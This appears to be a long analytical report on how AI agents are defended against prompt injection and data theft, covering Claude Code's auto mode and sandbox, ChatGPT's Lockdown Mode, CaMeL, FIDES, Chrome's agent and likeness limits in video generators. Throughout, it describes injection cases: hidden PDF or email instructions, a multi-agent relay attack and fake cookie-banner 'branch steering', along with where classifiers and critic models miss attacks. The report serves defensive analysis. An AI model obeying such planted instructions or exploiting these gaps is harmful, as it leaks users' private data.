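Willison's main objection to model-level defences is that an attacker can keep trying. In *Claude Opus 4.5, and why evaluating new LLMs is increasingly difficult*, Willison (2025) pointed out that about one attempt in 20 succeeded against Opus 4.5, and that ten attempts gave the attacker a one-in-three chance. Published figures show that newer models do much better.

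| Model | 1 attempt | 10 attempts | Most attempts reported |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 33.6% | 63.0% after 100 |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 0.1% | not given | 5–6% after 100 |
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 0.1% | 0.7% | 1.0% after 15 |

The Fable 5.1 figures come from a newer set of attacks, so the rows aren't strictly comparable. If each attempt succeeded independently with probability *p*, the chance of at least one success in *n* attempts would be 1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ, or about 9.5% for 100 attempts with *p* at 0.1%. The measured rate for Opus 4.7 is lower, presumably because a model that resists one attack in a given situation tends to resist similar ones.

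Anthropic notes that an attacker can also send the same hostile email to a thousand inboxes. At a success rate of 0.1%, one agent would obey on average. That rate is reassuring for any one user but much less so for a company with thousands of employees, where one stolen password may be enough for the attacker.

Attackers who adapt succeed even more often. In September 2026 Anthropic published tests in which attack software from Gray Swan had 200 attempts at each of 40 coding scenarios. It succeeded at least once in 31 scenarios against Fable 5.1, and in 18 when the probes were on. Gray Swan had trained the software on the same scenarios, using earlier Claude models. Anthropic calls these conditions deliberately permissive, because real attackers rarely know their target so well and each attempt could expose them.

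The best published result for auto mode comes from Trajectory Labs, which Anthropic commissioned to run 72 scenarios ten times each. In auto mode, none of the 720 attempts against each of the three Claude models succeeded. But with the permission checks bypassed, only 0.09% of attacks on Claude models succeeded, or about two in 2,160 if all three models are counted. The result is therefore mostly evidence of the models' own resistance, not of what auto mode adds. Another limitation is that Trajectory Labs developed the attacks against the older Opus 4.7.

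Willison (2026), in *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, agrees that the classifier is better than constant requests for approval, but notes that it still missed 11% of the dangerous commands in the tester study. He worries more about prompt injection than about accidental damage, and wants independent confirmation of Anthropic's prompt injection results. Less than three weeks later, Willison (2026) recounts in *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode*, Johann Rehberger reported an attack on auto mode that worked 80% of the time. *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary* reports that Rehberger's samples were small. It also reports that Anthropic called auto mode a convenience feature and said the real boundary was operating-system isolation combined with network control.

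Anthropic answers the general objection by saying that defences should overlap. In auto mode, an attack has to get past both the probe and the classifier. How much this helps depends on whether the two miss the same attacks. If each misses 10% and the misses are independent, 1% of attacks get past both, but if they miss the same attacks, 10% do. The February prompt would probably have passed both a probe that examines tool results and a classifier that checks for the user's consent, because the instruction came from the user. A network limit fails for different reasons, so it would probably add more protection than another classifier.

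Willison and Anthropic agree that enforced limits are stronger, and differ mainly over which protection should be on by default. In *Auto mode for Claude Code*, Willison (2026) asked for a sandbox by default because its restrictions on files and the network don't depend on a model's judgement. Anthropic advises developers to contain an agent's environment first and steer the model second. But according to its November 2026 documentation, Claude Code starts in auto mode, and users or their organisation have to turn the sandbox on.

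Anthropic offers an alternative to the sandbox because the sandbox needs upkeep. Each new tool may need its own configuration, and work that depends on the network or the rest of the computer can't run within its limits. This is a fair reason to make exceptions easy to configure but a weaker reason to leave the sandbox off, since, judging by the 84% figure, most routine work can probably run inside it.

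### What the sandbox leaves open

The built-in sandbox covers only shell commands and the programs they start. Claude's file tools follow separate permission rules, and Anthropic's *Choose a sandbox environment* says that some add-ons run without any sandbox restrictions. Anthropic therefore considers the built-in sandbox insufficient for unattended work and recommends running all of Claude Code in a container, a virtual machine or a wider version of the sandbox.

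Data can still leave through any approved domain, as it did in the upload leak from Cowork. The proxy checks the destination's name but doesn't decrypt the traffic, so it can't distinguish an ordinary download from the theft of a file. Companies can install a proxy that inspects the traffic, but they then have to manage its certificates.

Sandboxed programs also share the kernel, the central part of the operating system, with everything else on the computer. Anthropic's *Securely deploying AI agents* warns that a flaw in the kernel could let a program escape the sandbox. A virtual machine has its own kernel and isolates programs more strongly, but it uses more resources and takes more work to set up. None of these options protects the project itself if Claude has permission to change it.

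The sandbox can also be off without the developer noticing. If it can't start, Claude Code by default shows a warning and runs commands without it, though administrators can set Claude Code to stop instead. Some programming tools don't work inside the sandbox, so developers have to let them run outside it, which again relies on someone reading the request.

Manual approval remains useful when requests are few and stakes are high. *Running auto mode in production* (Vorwerck, 2026), an Anthropic article about satisfied customers, reports that Chad Kunsman, an engineer at the software company Gusto, switches out of auto mode when working on live systems and checks each action himself. Evan Magnussen, who manages platform engineering at Garner Health, lets the classifier decide on most actions but has configured it not to approve emails or Slack messages to other people.

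## ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode

Lockdown Mode is a ChatGPT setting that turns off or limits features that can contact outside servers. Like the sandbox in Claude Code, it is an enforced limit that users or their organisation have to turn on. OpenAI announced it for the Enterprise, Edu, Healthcare and Teachers plans on 13 February 2026, in *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*. On 4 June, OpenAI began extending it to personal accounts and to Business accounts that customers set up themselves. Free accounts can use it too, according to The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft*.

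OpenAI designed the mode to block the last step of a data theft, sending the data out. This is the only one of the three elements of the lethal trifecta that the mode restricts. Hidden instructions can still reach the model, and the model may still follow them. Willison (2026) likes this approach because, like a sandbox, it doesn't depend on a model's judgement.

### What the mode turns off

The table lists the features in OpenAI's help page *Lockdown Mode*. OpenAI says the general aim is to limit outgoing network requests, but it explains few of the individual choices, so the last column applies that aim to each feature. Deep research compiles reports from many websites, agent mode operates websites for the user, and Canvas is a workspace for editing text and code.

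| Feature | In Lockdown Mode | Can it send a request to an outside server? |
|---|---|---|
| Web browsing | Saved copies of pages only | Live browsing can, but reading a saved copy doesn't |
| Web images in answers | May not appear | Yes, to the server that holds the image |
| Deep research | Off | Yes, to the sites it consults |
| Agent mode | Off | Yes, and it can also fill in forms |
| Network access for Canvas code | Off | Yes, to any address in the code |
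| File downloads by ChatGPT | Off | Yes, to the server that holds the file |
| Files the user uploads | Unchanged | No, the file goes to OpenAI |
| Image generation | Unchanged | No, OpenAI's own systems make the picture |
| Memory | Unchanged | No, OpenAI stores it |
| Sharing a conversation | Unchanged | No, the user decides to share it |
| Codex | Unchanged | Yes, if the developer allows it |

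Codex can contact outside servers, but developers control its network access through settings separate from Lockdown Mode, including a list of permitted domains. Lockdown Mode therefore doesn't protect confidential files that someone opens in Codex. This matters because PromptArmor's Google Forms attack worked against Codex in April 2026.

When ChatGPT reads a saved copy of a page, no live request leaves OpenAI's network, so the site's owner can't learn which page it read. This stops attackers from spelling out a secret through ChatGPT's choice of pages, an attack that the public-address check doesn't prevent. However, search results may be out of date or missing.

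Loading a web image can send private data to an attacker's server, as in the payslip example. But if hidden instructions make ChatGPT generate a picture with the user's salary written on it, the picture appears in the user's chat, where the attacker can't see it. This is probably why Lockdown Mode leaves image generation on, though OpenAI doesn't give a reason.

An uploaded file can still mislead the model, because the model has to read the file to use it. For example, a supplier could send a contract with hidden text telling AI systems to describe the cancellation terms as standard, and ChatGPT might then leave a large penalty out of its summary. Blocking outgoing requests wouldn't prevent this, because the supplier benefits without receiving any data. OpenAI warns that hidden instructions in uploaded files and saved web pages can cause wrong answers in Lockdown Mode.

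### Connected apps

Apps connect ChatGPT to other services, such as a company's document store. On personal and self-serve Business accounts, OpenAI decides what apps can do in Lockdown Mode. In June, ChatGPT could use data that OpenAI had already copied from a service, but it couldn't contact the service live or change anything there, according to Help Net Security's *OpenAI is locking down parts of ChatGPT to reduce data theft risks*. OpenAI now describes a less strict rule, under which it blocks live access and write actions "when those actions conflict with its security protections". ChatGPT's personal finance and shopping-agent features are unavailable in Lockdown Mode.

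In workspaces that an organisation's administrators manage, Lockdown Mode doesn't automatically turn off every app. OpenAI lets administrators choose which apps, and which actions within each app, stay available, because some important work depends on them. The protection therefore depends partly on how carefully administrators choose.

Workspace owners turn the mode on by assigning a Lockdown Mode role to members or groups. OpenAI's *Managing feature access with role-based access control in ChatGPT* explains that a member with several ordinary roles can use a feature if any one of them grants it. A Lockdown Mode role overrides those roles. If an employee's research role allows live web search and their Lockdown Mode role restricts it, the restriction applies. This is sensible because adding someone to another group can't accidentally remove their protection.

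OpenAI ranks app actions by the risk that they could help an attacker steal data:

| Action | Risk | Main concern |
|---|---|---|
| Reading or writing in an untrusted app | High | The app's operator may receive private data |
| Writing in a trusted app when outsiders might see the result | High | An attacker may read what ChatGPT wrote |
| Writing in a trusted app when only trusted people can see the result | Medium | Someone may be wrong about who can see it |
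| Reading in a trusted app | Medium | ChatGPT obtains private data that could leak by another route |
| Searching an index that administrators manage | Medium | The index may contain private data, though searching it can avoid a live request |

OpenAI doesn't explain why it considers even reading high-risk in an untrusted app, but the app's operator can see what ChatGPT searches for, and hidden instructions could make ChatGPT put private data in the search terms. For trusted apps, the risk ranking depends mostly on who can see the result.

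Suppose a finance director asks ChatGPT to summarise a PDF from outside the company. Hidden instructions in the PDF tell ChatGPT to find the price the company plans to offer for a competitor and add it to a page in the company's document service. If only three colleagues can open the page, the attacker learns nothing, although someone has to notice the figure and delete it. If the page is a public help page, the attacker can read the price by visiting it.

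Both requests go to the same trusted service, from the same account, and perform the same kind of action, so the destination and account checks that Anthropic added to Cowork would allow both. An administrator who wants ChatGPT to edit private documents therefore has to find out whether the same permission covers public pages. If it does, the company can leave the action off or remove the director's right to edit public pages in the document service, whose permissions ChatGPT can't override.

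A private document may later become public when a colleague shares it with a customer, and some services email new comments to everyone following a page, including people outside the company. OpenAI advises administrators not to enable a write action unless they can confirm that an attacker won't see its effects.

### Administrators' control over uploads

An uploaded file may contain hidden instructions, or it may be a confidential file that the company doesn't want an AI provider to hold. Lockdown Mode doesn't stop employees from uploading confidential files to ChatGPT, because it doesn't change how uploads work.

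OpenAI says workspace administrators can separately configure "many" of the settings that Lockdown Mode leaves unchanged, which include uploads, memory and sharing. OpenAI's *Managing workspace settings in ChatGPT Enterprise* lists controls for memory, link sharing, Canvas and apps, but no control for file uploads. *Feature controls and integrations with your tools* (2025), an OpenAI guide for administrators last updated in September 2026, doesn't list one either. A company that needs to block uploads should ask OpenAI whether it can.

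Microsoft 365 Copilot has a more clearly defined control. In the thread *Prevent data loss when using Copilot in your company*, a Microsoft moderator told a user called hehe (2026) in March 2026 that an organisation can allow uploads everywhere, block them everywhere, or allow them only in Copilot's Work mode, which draws on the organisation's own data. With the third option, employees can upload a report to compare it with internal documents, but can't upload it in Web mode or Copilot Chat. Administrators have to ask Microsoft Support to apply these settings, according to the moderator.

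The user had asked for something narrower, a limit on which addresses employees could use for uploads, because they worried that someone signed in to a personal account could cause a data leak. None of the three options provides that. The moderator also recommended Microsoft's audit log, which can show file-related actions afterwards but doesn't prevent them. ChatGPT Enterprise partly solves this problem by letting workspace owners stop members from switching between work and personal accounts within ChatGPT. That should reduce mistakes, though a determined employee could presumably sign in to a personal account in another browser.

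Blocking uploads also offers limited protection for confidential data, because employees can paste text from a file into the chat. It would prevent much legitimate work too, particularly in Lockdown Mode, where uploading is the main way to give ChatGPT a file from the web.

### Who should use it

In Lockdown Mode, ChatGPT can't book a flight, compare today's prices or write a deep research report. Other tasks take more effort. For instance, ChatGPT can't download a government spreadsheet to analyse, but the user can download it and upload it to the chat. Work with material the user already has, such as redrafting a letter or checking a set of accounts, is mostly unaffected.

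In February, OpenAI said the mode was "not necessary for most users". It had designed the mode for a small group facing advanced threats, such as executives and security teams at prominent organisations. Dane Stuckey, OpenAI's chief information security officer, said in June that losing features was worthwhile for people who are at higher risk because of who they are, what they work on or what data they handle.

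This reasoning is strongest for attacks aimed at a particular person, but a hostile web page or file can affect anyone whose assistant reads it. Most of the attacks on Copilot, Superhuman and Claude would have worked on ordinary users. Willison concludes from the mode's existence that ChatGPT's default settings don't protect reliably against a determined attacker. OpenAI partly concedes this by labelling some network features "Elevated Risk", because the industry's safeguards don't yet fully address their risks. Its advice to most users is therefore best understood as weighing inconvenience against risk. For someone who mainly asks ChatGPT about recipes and football, losing live search is a daily nuisance, while data theft is unlikely and might reveal little.

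In June, OpenAI broadened its description of the mode, also recommending it for times when users would accept fewer features in return for stricter protection. That suits people who handle sensitive material only occasionally. On personal and self-serve Business accounts, users can keep the mode on and turn it off for a single chat, for example to research a holiday.

Turning Lockdown Mode off for one chat creates two risks. Lockdown Mode doesn't change memory, so details that ChatGPT remembers from a protected chat could presumably be available in an unprotected one, where an attacker could try to extract them. Users who handle very sensitive data can reduce this risk by turning memory off. A user could also be tricked into turning Lockdown Mode off, much as the Anthropic employee was tricked into running a harmful prompt.

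### The remaining risk

OpenAI doesn't guarantee that Lockdown Mode will prevent every leak. It says data could still get out through apps that remain enabled, unexpected combinations of features, or new techniques. OpenAI's announcement and help page give no attack success rates with the mode on or off, so it's unclear how much the mode helps.

The security company Check Point found a flaw that let attackers extract chat data despite Lockdown Mode, according to The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026). OpenAI fixed the flaw on 18 September 2026, and the findings became public in early November.

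## CaMeL and Chrome's agent: permissions that follow the data

Lockdown Mode can't distinguish an edit that publishes a confidential price from one that only colleagues can read. A finer limit depends on properties of the data, such as where it came from and who may see it. CaMeL, a research system that Debenedetti and colleagues described in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), works this way. It partly inspired Google's design for Chrome's agent.

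CaMeL borrows the word "capability" from an older idea in computer security, where it means an unforgeable token that gives its holder a specific right to a specific object, such as the right to read one file. A program that holds only this token can't open any other file, even if the user who started the program could. CaMeL instead attaches permissions to the data. Each value has a tag that records its source and who may read it, and software checks the tags before the agent acts.

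### How CaMeL works

CaMeL builds on Willison's "dual LLM" pattern from 2023, which uses one language model to plan actions and a separate one to read untrusted text. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, describe the procedure, which runs roughly as follows:

1. The planning model receives the user's request and a description of the tools. It writes a short Python program containing every tool call the task might need.
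2. An interpreter, which is ordinary software outside both models, runs the program. It stores whatever the tools return in variables that the planning model never sees.
3. If the program needs something from untrusted text, such as a summary, the interpreter gives the text to the reading model. This model has no tools and can only return a value.
4. The interpreter tracks which earlier values each new value depends on, so a summary of an email still counts as coming from that email.
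5. Before every tool call, the interpreter checks the tags against a policy and blocks the call if the policy forbids it.

Suppose a user asks the agent to send `budget.xlsx` to Dana, a colleague, with a summary of a supplier's latest email. Hidden text in the email instructs the agent to send the budget to an outside address too. The planning model never reads the email, so its program contains one sending step, with Dana's address taken from the user's request. The hidden text might distort the summary, but it can't add a recipient.

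Now suppose the user asks the agent to send the file to whoever requested it in yesterday's email. The program has to take the address from the email, so an attacker who wrote that email can choose the recipient without changing the plan. The policy then has to stop the transfer. *CaMeLoT* (2026), an extension of CaMeL, explains that separating the two models protects against attacks on the plan, and that the capabilities protect against attacks on the data.

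A deployer could allow the transfer if the address came from the user, or if the recipient is already allowed to read the file:

| Source of the address | Recipient may already read the file | Recipient may not read the file |
|---|---|---|
| The user's request | Sent | Sent, because the user chose the recipient |
| An email | Sent | Blocked, or sent only if the user approves |

A destination allowlist like the one for Claude's programs would treat all four cases alike if they used the same mail server. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) points out that sandboxes have the same limitation, since an injected prompt can make an agent leak data in a plausible message if the agent may send email at all.

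### How well CaMeL performs

Researchers usually test these systems on *AgentDojo* (2024), a benchmark with 97 ordinary tasks and 70 tools in simulated office, Slack, banking and travel settings. The benchmark hides attackers' instructions in the material that the agent reads. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) reports that CaMeL stopped nearly all attacks in its original tests, with comparable task performance. Later tests by other teams support the security claim but show a much larger drop in completed tasks.

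In *SecureClaw* (2026), none of 629 attacks succeeded against CaMeL's released code, but the agent completed only 29 of the 97 tasks when there was no attack. The SecureClaw system completed 59. *Kairos* (2026) tested CaMeL with its policies on, using two different models. Attacks succeeded 0.2% and 0.4% of the time, and CaMeL completed 38% and 40% of tasks when there was no attack. With the same models, a defence called Progent completed 78% and 82%, but 11.5% and 5.4% of attacks succeeded.

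SecureClaw and Kairos are rival defences to CaMeL, and the SecureClaw team had to adapt CaMeL's code to run it, so a better-tuned version of CaMeL might complete more tasks. CaMeL's planning model has to write code to handle a tool's results before seeing any, which is a known difficulty. Peters-Gill and colleagues had to add a full description of each tool's output format to get reasonable performance.

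They then tested CaMeL in teams of agents, with no policies set. Across five models, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL and 0.2% with it. Without CaMeL, the rate ranged from zero for GPT-5.5 to 36.1% for the older GPT-4.1. Stronger attacks might still work on GPT-5.5. *Bounded Agents* (2026) cites a competition with 272,000 attacks in which all 13 frontier models obeyed some of the attacks, at rates between 0.5% and 8.5%.

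On a separate benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks, CaMeL lowered the completion rate by 21.6 percentage points on average, but by 13.4 points for the two strongest models. This drop may therefore shrink as models get better at planning. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) report in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* that defences of this kind also use more tokens, the units of text that models process.

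The attacks that still worked all exploited the way agents pass messages to one another. Peters-Gill and colleagues demonstrated this with agents that were all running CaMeL. They asked a coordinating agent to send a summary of job applicants to Julie on Slack. One agent fetched the records, which contained an instruction to email the data to an outsider. The coordinating agent pasted the summary into its request to a third agent, whose planning model treated the whole request as coming from its user and added the email to its plan. A policy that trusts addresses supplied by the user might not have helped, because the attacker's address now appeared to come from the user.

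The researchers fixed this by sending instructions and data between agents separately and hiding the data from the receiving agent's planning model. After that, no attacks succeeded. The fix lowered average task completion on the maintenance benchmark by another 3.2 points.

### Microsoft's FIDES

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a similar system from Microsoft. FIDES labels each piece of data with whether it is trusted and who may read it. Data made from several sources keeps the restrictions of all of them. If Ann, Bob and Carla may read one document and Bob, Carla and Dev may read another, only Bob and Carla may read a summary of both. If either document is untrusted, so is the summary.

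CaMeL fixes its plan before any tool results come in, whereas FIDES plans one step at a time and hides a result from the planning model only if reading it would make the model's security labels more restrictive. The model can open a hidden result if it needs to. FIDES then treats the model's later decisions as influenced by untrusted text, and the policy can block consequential actions such as payments.

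FIDES can also query an isolated model and limit its answer to a fixed set, such as yes or no to whether an email requests a meeting. A yes-or-no answer carries at most one bit, which is too little to hold an attacker's instructions, so a policy could let the agent act on it.

The researchers tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. The completion rates below are averages over the four settings, without an attack.

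| Agent | Tasks completed | Successful attacks |
|---|---:|---:|
| Ordinary agent, no policies | 84% | 152 |
| Ordinary agent with policies | 42% | 0 |
| FIDES, no policies | 61% | 21 |
| FIDES with policies | 50% | 0 |

The policies stopped the attacks in both agents, and hiding untrusted results recovered some of the lost tasks. With o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES's lead over the ordinary agent with policies grew from 8 to 16 points. FIDES's calls to the isolated model add time and tokens, but Costa and colleagues didn't measure how much.

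The zeros need qualification. AgentDojo's scoring counted three successful attacks against FIDES with policies, but the researchers discounted them after checking them by hand. They discounted an attack if, for example, the policies permitted the action. They had also labelled as untrusted every type of field that the benchmark's attacks use, but a deployer doesn't know in advance where attacks will appear.

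Kolluri and colleagues, also mostly at Microsoft, object to the usual comparison of completed tasks. In that comparison, the ordinary agent may take any action without asking, while the protected agent gets no human help when a policy blocks it. Many products ask for approval before consequential actions, so the researchers also count approvals. They built an agent called Prudentia on top of FIDES and told its planning model about the labels and policies. On AgentDojo, FIDES needed up to 1.9 times as many approvals as Prudentia.

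### Chrome's separation of sites

Browsers enforce a same-origin policy, which stops a script on one origin from reading data from another. An origin is the combination of protocol, host name and port in a web address. A browsing agent can get around the policy because it can read a bank page and then type what it read into a form on another site.

Wang, Chen and colleagues tested this with simulated websites in *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers* (2026). An agent handled private information on one site and then visited another that contained hidden instructions. ChatGPT Atlas, OpenAI's browser, copied the exact private data to the second site in 99 of 150 runs.

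Google's published design for Chrome limits which sites the agent can use for each task. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes two sets of origins. The agent may read pages from read-only origins, and may also click and type on read-writable ones. If a user asks the agent to add a recipe's ingredients to a supermarket basket, the recipe site could be read-only and the supermarket read-writable. A hostile comment under the recipe couldn't then make the agent post the user's address on an unrelated forum.

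Chrome also hides embedded frames, such as adverts, if their origin isn't in either set. This can prevent accidental leaks as well as attacks. When Wang and colleagues asked the open-source browser BrowserOS to summarise a page and write the summary in a text box on the same page, it included private data from an embedded frame every time.

Unlike CaMeL's planner, Chrome's main planning model reads web pages. Google relies on a second model, the User Alignment Critic, to veto actions that don't serve the user's goal. The critic sees only information about the proposed action, so text on a web page can't reach it directly. A variant of the critic decides whether a new site is relevant to the task. The browser can enforce the sets of sites, but a model decides which sites go into them.

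Chrome, like ChatGPT, also restricts model-written addresses to known public ones. It asks the user before the agent opens certain sensitive sites or signs in with a saved password, and it is meant to ask before the agent makes a purchase or sends a message.

The first version of Chrome's site limits tracked only the read-writable set, so it did not separate reading from acting. Google said it would adjust the system after seeing how it affected users' tasks. Parker gives no attack success rates or figures for how often the limits block legitimate work. The published test results for CaMeL and FIDES come from research code and simulated tasks, whereas billions of people use Chrome.

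Site separation also can't stop a leak within one site. In the supermarket example, an injected instruction could make the agent put the user's home address in a public product review. The supermarket is read-writable, so the sets allow this, although the critic might veto it.

### Who writes the labels and policies

To stop leaks within a site, software needs information about which parts of a page are private and which parts strangers wrote. *SPIDES* (Zverev, Kim and colleagues, 2026) proposes that website operators supply it in the page's code. A shop would mark customer reviews as untrusted and a saved card number as readable only by the user and the shop. The user keeps a list of sites whose labels they trust.

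Zverev and colleagues tested SPIDES on 28 simulated websites with five models. They assumed the worst case, in which the attacker controls the model's output whenever it has read hostile text. None of the 56 attacks succeeded, and SPIDES completed 67% to 86% of tasks, depending on the model. SOPGuard, a defence by Wang and colleagues that asks the user before data moves between sites, let through 53% to 73% of the attacks.

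The simulated sites were labelled correctly throughout, but real sites might not be. SPIDES treats anything unlabelled on a trusted site as trusted and public. If a shop forgets to label its reviews, any reviewer can give the agent instructions. The researchers compare labelling a site to adding accessibility information, which many sites already provide. But operators may have little reason to add labels until popular browsers use them.

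SPIDES also needed an average of 1.84 approvals per completed task. The test assumed a user who always recognises an unsafe request, but judging by Anthropic's tester study, real users would probably let some attacks through.

Policies are hard to write even when the labels are right. Peters-Gill and colleagues left policies out of their tests because any choice among the many possible ones would have been arbitrary and would have affected the results, but a deployer has to choose. Policies are especially hard to write for agents that operate a whole computer, because a click can log in, delete data or open a hostile site depending on what is under the pointer.

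Peters-Gill and colleagues acknowledge that CaMeL's interpreter, which tracks the labels, can also miss some indirect influences. If untrusted text determines whether a program changes a variable, the variable may keep its trusted label.

### Tasks that depend on untrusted text

Some users want the agent to follow instructions in a document, such as how to pay a bill. Costa and colleagues found that about 43% of AgentDojo's Slack tasks and 44% of its banking tasks depend on what the agent reads, compared with 5% of its office tasks. FIDES blocks many of the banking tasks once the agent has read the file. This can block payment of a genuine bill, because the labels can't distinguish it from a forged one.

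Prudentia lets the user approve a document instead of each action. For example, the user can approve an email containing a ten-item to-do list once instead of ten times. This saves time, but it makes that one decision much more important, and the user may not notice instructions hidden in white text.

CaMeL is less able to adapt because it writes the whole plan in advance. In some of Peters-Gill and colleagues' tests, an agent couldn't find data for the requested period and returned data for a nearby one. The plan had no step to check for this, so the coordinating agent carried on with the wrong data.

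Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, tried to solve this for agents that work from screenshots. Their planning model prepares for many possible screens, such as one with a cookie banner. The plans averaged 41 tool calls, compared with about five for AgentDojo. The system kept at most 57% of the performance of frontier models without this protection.

### Harm without a forbidden transfer

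An attacker can also do harm through steps that the plan already contains. Foerster and colleagues put a fake cookie banner inside an advert, and the agent clicked it because closing cookie banners was part of its plan. The click took the agent to the attacker's site. They call this attack branch steering.

False information can get through too. Costa and colleagues give the example of an email that makes the isolated model return an empty summary, which FIDES would then send to the right person. A policy could also require the message text to be trusted, but then the agent couldn't send summaries of outside emails. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) tested another system that tracks data in code. In one case, an agent booked the hotel the user wanted but also repeated a planted recommendation for a different one. The policy allowed this because the reviews were public.

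An agent's choices can reveal private information even when it sends none directly. *AgentTell* (2026) tested six models in 9,760 sessions and found such leaks even with no hostile content and the same-origin policy intact. For example, if an agent has seen a pharmacy order and then picks only sugar-free food, the shop might guess that the user has diabetes. FIDES's guarantee doesn't cover what an observer can infer from the agent's sequence of actions.

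CaMeL and FIDES also trust the user's request. Costa and colleagues reason that if no untrusted text influenced a transfer, the system can assume the user intended it. Anthropic's February exercise is a counterexample. The rule in the table of recipients would have allowed the theft, because the attacker's address came from the deceived user. The labels also wouldn't stop a user who deliberately asks for a fake recording of a real person. They track where data came from and who may read it, but the harm is in what the recording contains.

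## Video and voice generators: limits set before release

Developers of video and voice generators try to prevent fake recordings of real people by limiting who can appear or speak in the output. Google and OpenAI set many of these limits before release, when they had test results but little experience of how the public would use the products. They rely on five kinds of limit.

| Limit | How it works | How it can fail |
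|---|---|---|
| Setting | Each request carries a value, such as "adults only" | The available values may not fit a legitimate use |
| Fixed menu | The user picks from voices the company has prepared | A voice on the menu may resemble a real person's |
| Upload check | Software inspects a photo or recording before the generator uses it | It may misjudge who a person is, or how old |
| Consent record | The system stores a person's agreement to the use of their likeness | Someone may give consent on another person's behalf |
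| Output check | A classifier examines the finished video or speech | It may misjudge the content |

The system can err by letting harmful material through (missed harm) or by blocking something legitimate (wrongful refusal). Making a classifier stricter usually reduces missed harm but increases wrongful refusal.

### Google's setting for people in Veo

Veo is a Google model that generates videos of up to eight seconds, with sound in recent versions. Developers who build on it can control whether people appear through a setting called `personGeneration`. The value `dont_allow` excludes people, `allow_adult` permits only adults, and `allow_all` also permits children. Google's *Generate videos with Veo 3.1 in Gemini API* gave the following permitted values in July 2026:

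| Request | Veo 2 | Veo 3 and 3.1 |
|---|---|---|
| Text only, most regions | Any of the three | `allow_all` |
| Text with a starting image, most regions | `dont_allow` or `allow_adult` | `allow_adult` |
| Any request from the EU, UK, Switzerland, Middle East or North Africa | `dont_allow` (default) or `allow_adult` | `allow_adult` |

One of Google's sample prompts is for a close-up of a girl holding a golden retriever puppy in a park. A developer in Texas can send this as a text prompt because the `allow_all` setting covers children. A developer in Germany can use only `allow_adult`, so Veo should refuse the prompt. If the girl is changed to a woman, the prompt should work in both places.

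The developer in Texas is also limited to generating adults when starting from a photograph of the girl. Google doesn't explain why it treats photographs differently from text prompts, but a photograph may well show a real child, while a text prompt usually produces an invented one.

On Veo 3.1, the setting has only one permitted value for each kind of request. With Veo 2, which Google has deprecated, the maker of a geography app could use `dont_allow` to keep people out of its landscapes. On Veo 3.1, the app's maker would have to ask for landscapes without people in the prompt, which is only an instructed limit.

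Google's platform for business customers adds two filters, according to Google Cloud's *Responsible AI and usage guidelines*. One rejects requests to depict children unless the developer has chosen `allow_all` and Google has put the project on an allowlist. The other rejects photorealistic depictions of prominent people, except for approved projects on an allowlist. The error message includes a code that identifies which filter blocked the request.

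The rules don't always work as documented. In July 2026, a developer in one of the restricted regions reported that Veo was rejecting `allow_adult`, the only value the documentation allowed there, as "currently not supported" (*Request allowlist access for Veo 3.1 person generation*).

### Different rules in Google's newer model

Google's *Video generation in the Gemini API* now recommends another model, Gemini Omni Flash, for most video work, and Veo 3.1 for particular features. Omni's limits depend more on what the user uploads. In August 2026, Google didn't let users in the European Economic Area, Switzerland or the UK upload images of minors, or edit or extend their own videos. It also barred users everywhere from uploading images of "certain recognizable people".

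In those countries, Omni can still edit videos that it generated. Someone in Paris can change the lighting in a generated clip but not in one filmed on a phone. A ban on all uploaded video is easy to enforce because it doesn't require a classifier to identify the people in a clip, but it also stops users from editing footage with no people in it, such as a video of an empty beach.

Whether a request is allowed can depend on the model. Veo 3.1 accepts only adults in starting images, wherever the developer is. Omni bans images of minors only in some regions, which implies that the developer in Texas could use Omni to animate the photograph of the girl.

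### Sora 2's rules at launch

OpenAI released Sora 2, its video and audio generator, with a social app on 30 September 2025. The *Sora 2 System Card* (2025) describes stricter launch rules than Google's. OpenAI restricted all video uploads and uploads of photos showing realistic people. It didn't allow users to generate public figures from text, and it blocked depictions of any real person who hadn't agreed through a feature called cameo. OpenAI had also limited uploads of people when it launched the first Sora, according to the company's *Sora is here*.

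To create a cameo, a person recorded themselves in the app and then chose who could use their likeness. They could withdraw permission later. They could also see and delete any video that included them, even another user's unpublished draft, so they could check how others were using their likeness. But withdrawing permission didn't remove copies that someone had already downloaded.

Before Sora made a video, classifiers examined the prompt and any image, and could block the request. After Sora made the video, other software examined its frames, a transcript of its sound and a written description of the scene. This software included a model that OpenAI had trained to reason about its content policies. OpenAI applied stricter thresholds to users who might be under 18, and to videos based on uploads that seemed to show a minor.

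Such checks enforce a company's rules, so they don't help when the rules leave something out. OpenAI allowed videos of historical figures, then paused depictions of Martin Luther King Jr. in October 2025 after his estate objected to disrespectful ones.

### From the subject's consent to the uploader's word

By March 2026, OpenAI had relaxed the rule on photographs. Its *Creating with Sora safely* (2026) explains that users could make videos from pictures of family and friends after declaring that the people shown had consented. Cameos, which OpenAI had renamed "characters", remained available.

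The declaration was a much weaker safeguard than a cameo, because it came from the uploader. An abusive former partner could make it, and the person in the photo might never find out. OpenAI partly compensated by applying stricter content checks to these videos than to those made with characters, and stricter ones still when the photo showed a child or someone who looked young. It also watermarked every such video that a user shared. The checks could block a sexual video of a former partner, but software would find it harder to recognise a video that was merely false or humiliating.

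There was little time to see how the new rule worked, because OpenAI announced on 24 March, the day after it published the page, that it would close Sora. Axios' *OpenAI to discontinue Sora video app* (2026) reports that Sora was using a lot of computing power and that OpenAI wanted to focus on fewer products. AP's *OpenAI pulls the plug on Sora* (2026) notes that the app had also alarmed people in Hollywood. The reasons Axios gives are commercial, so the closure isn't good evidence that the likeness rules had failed.

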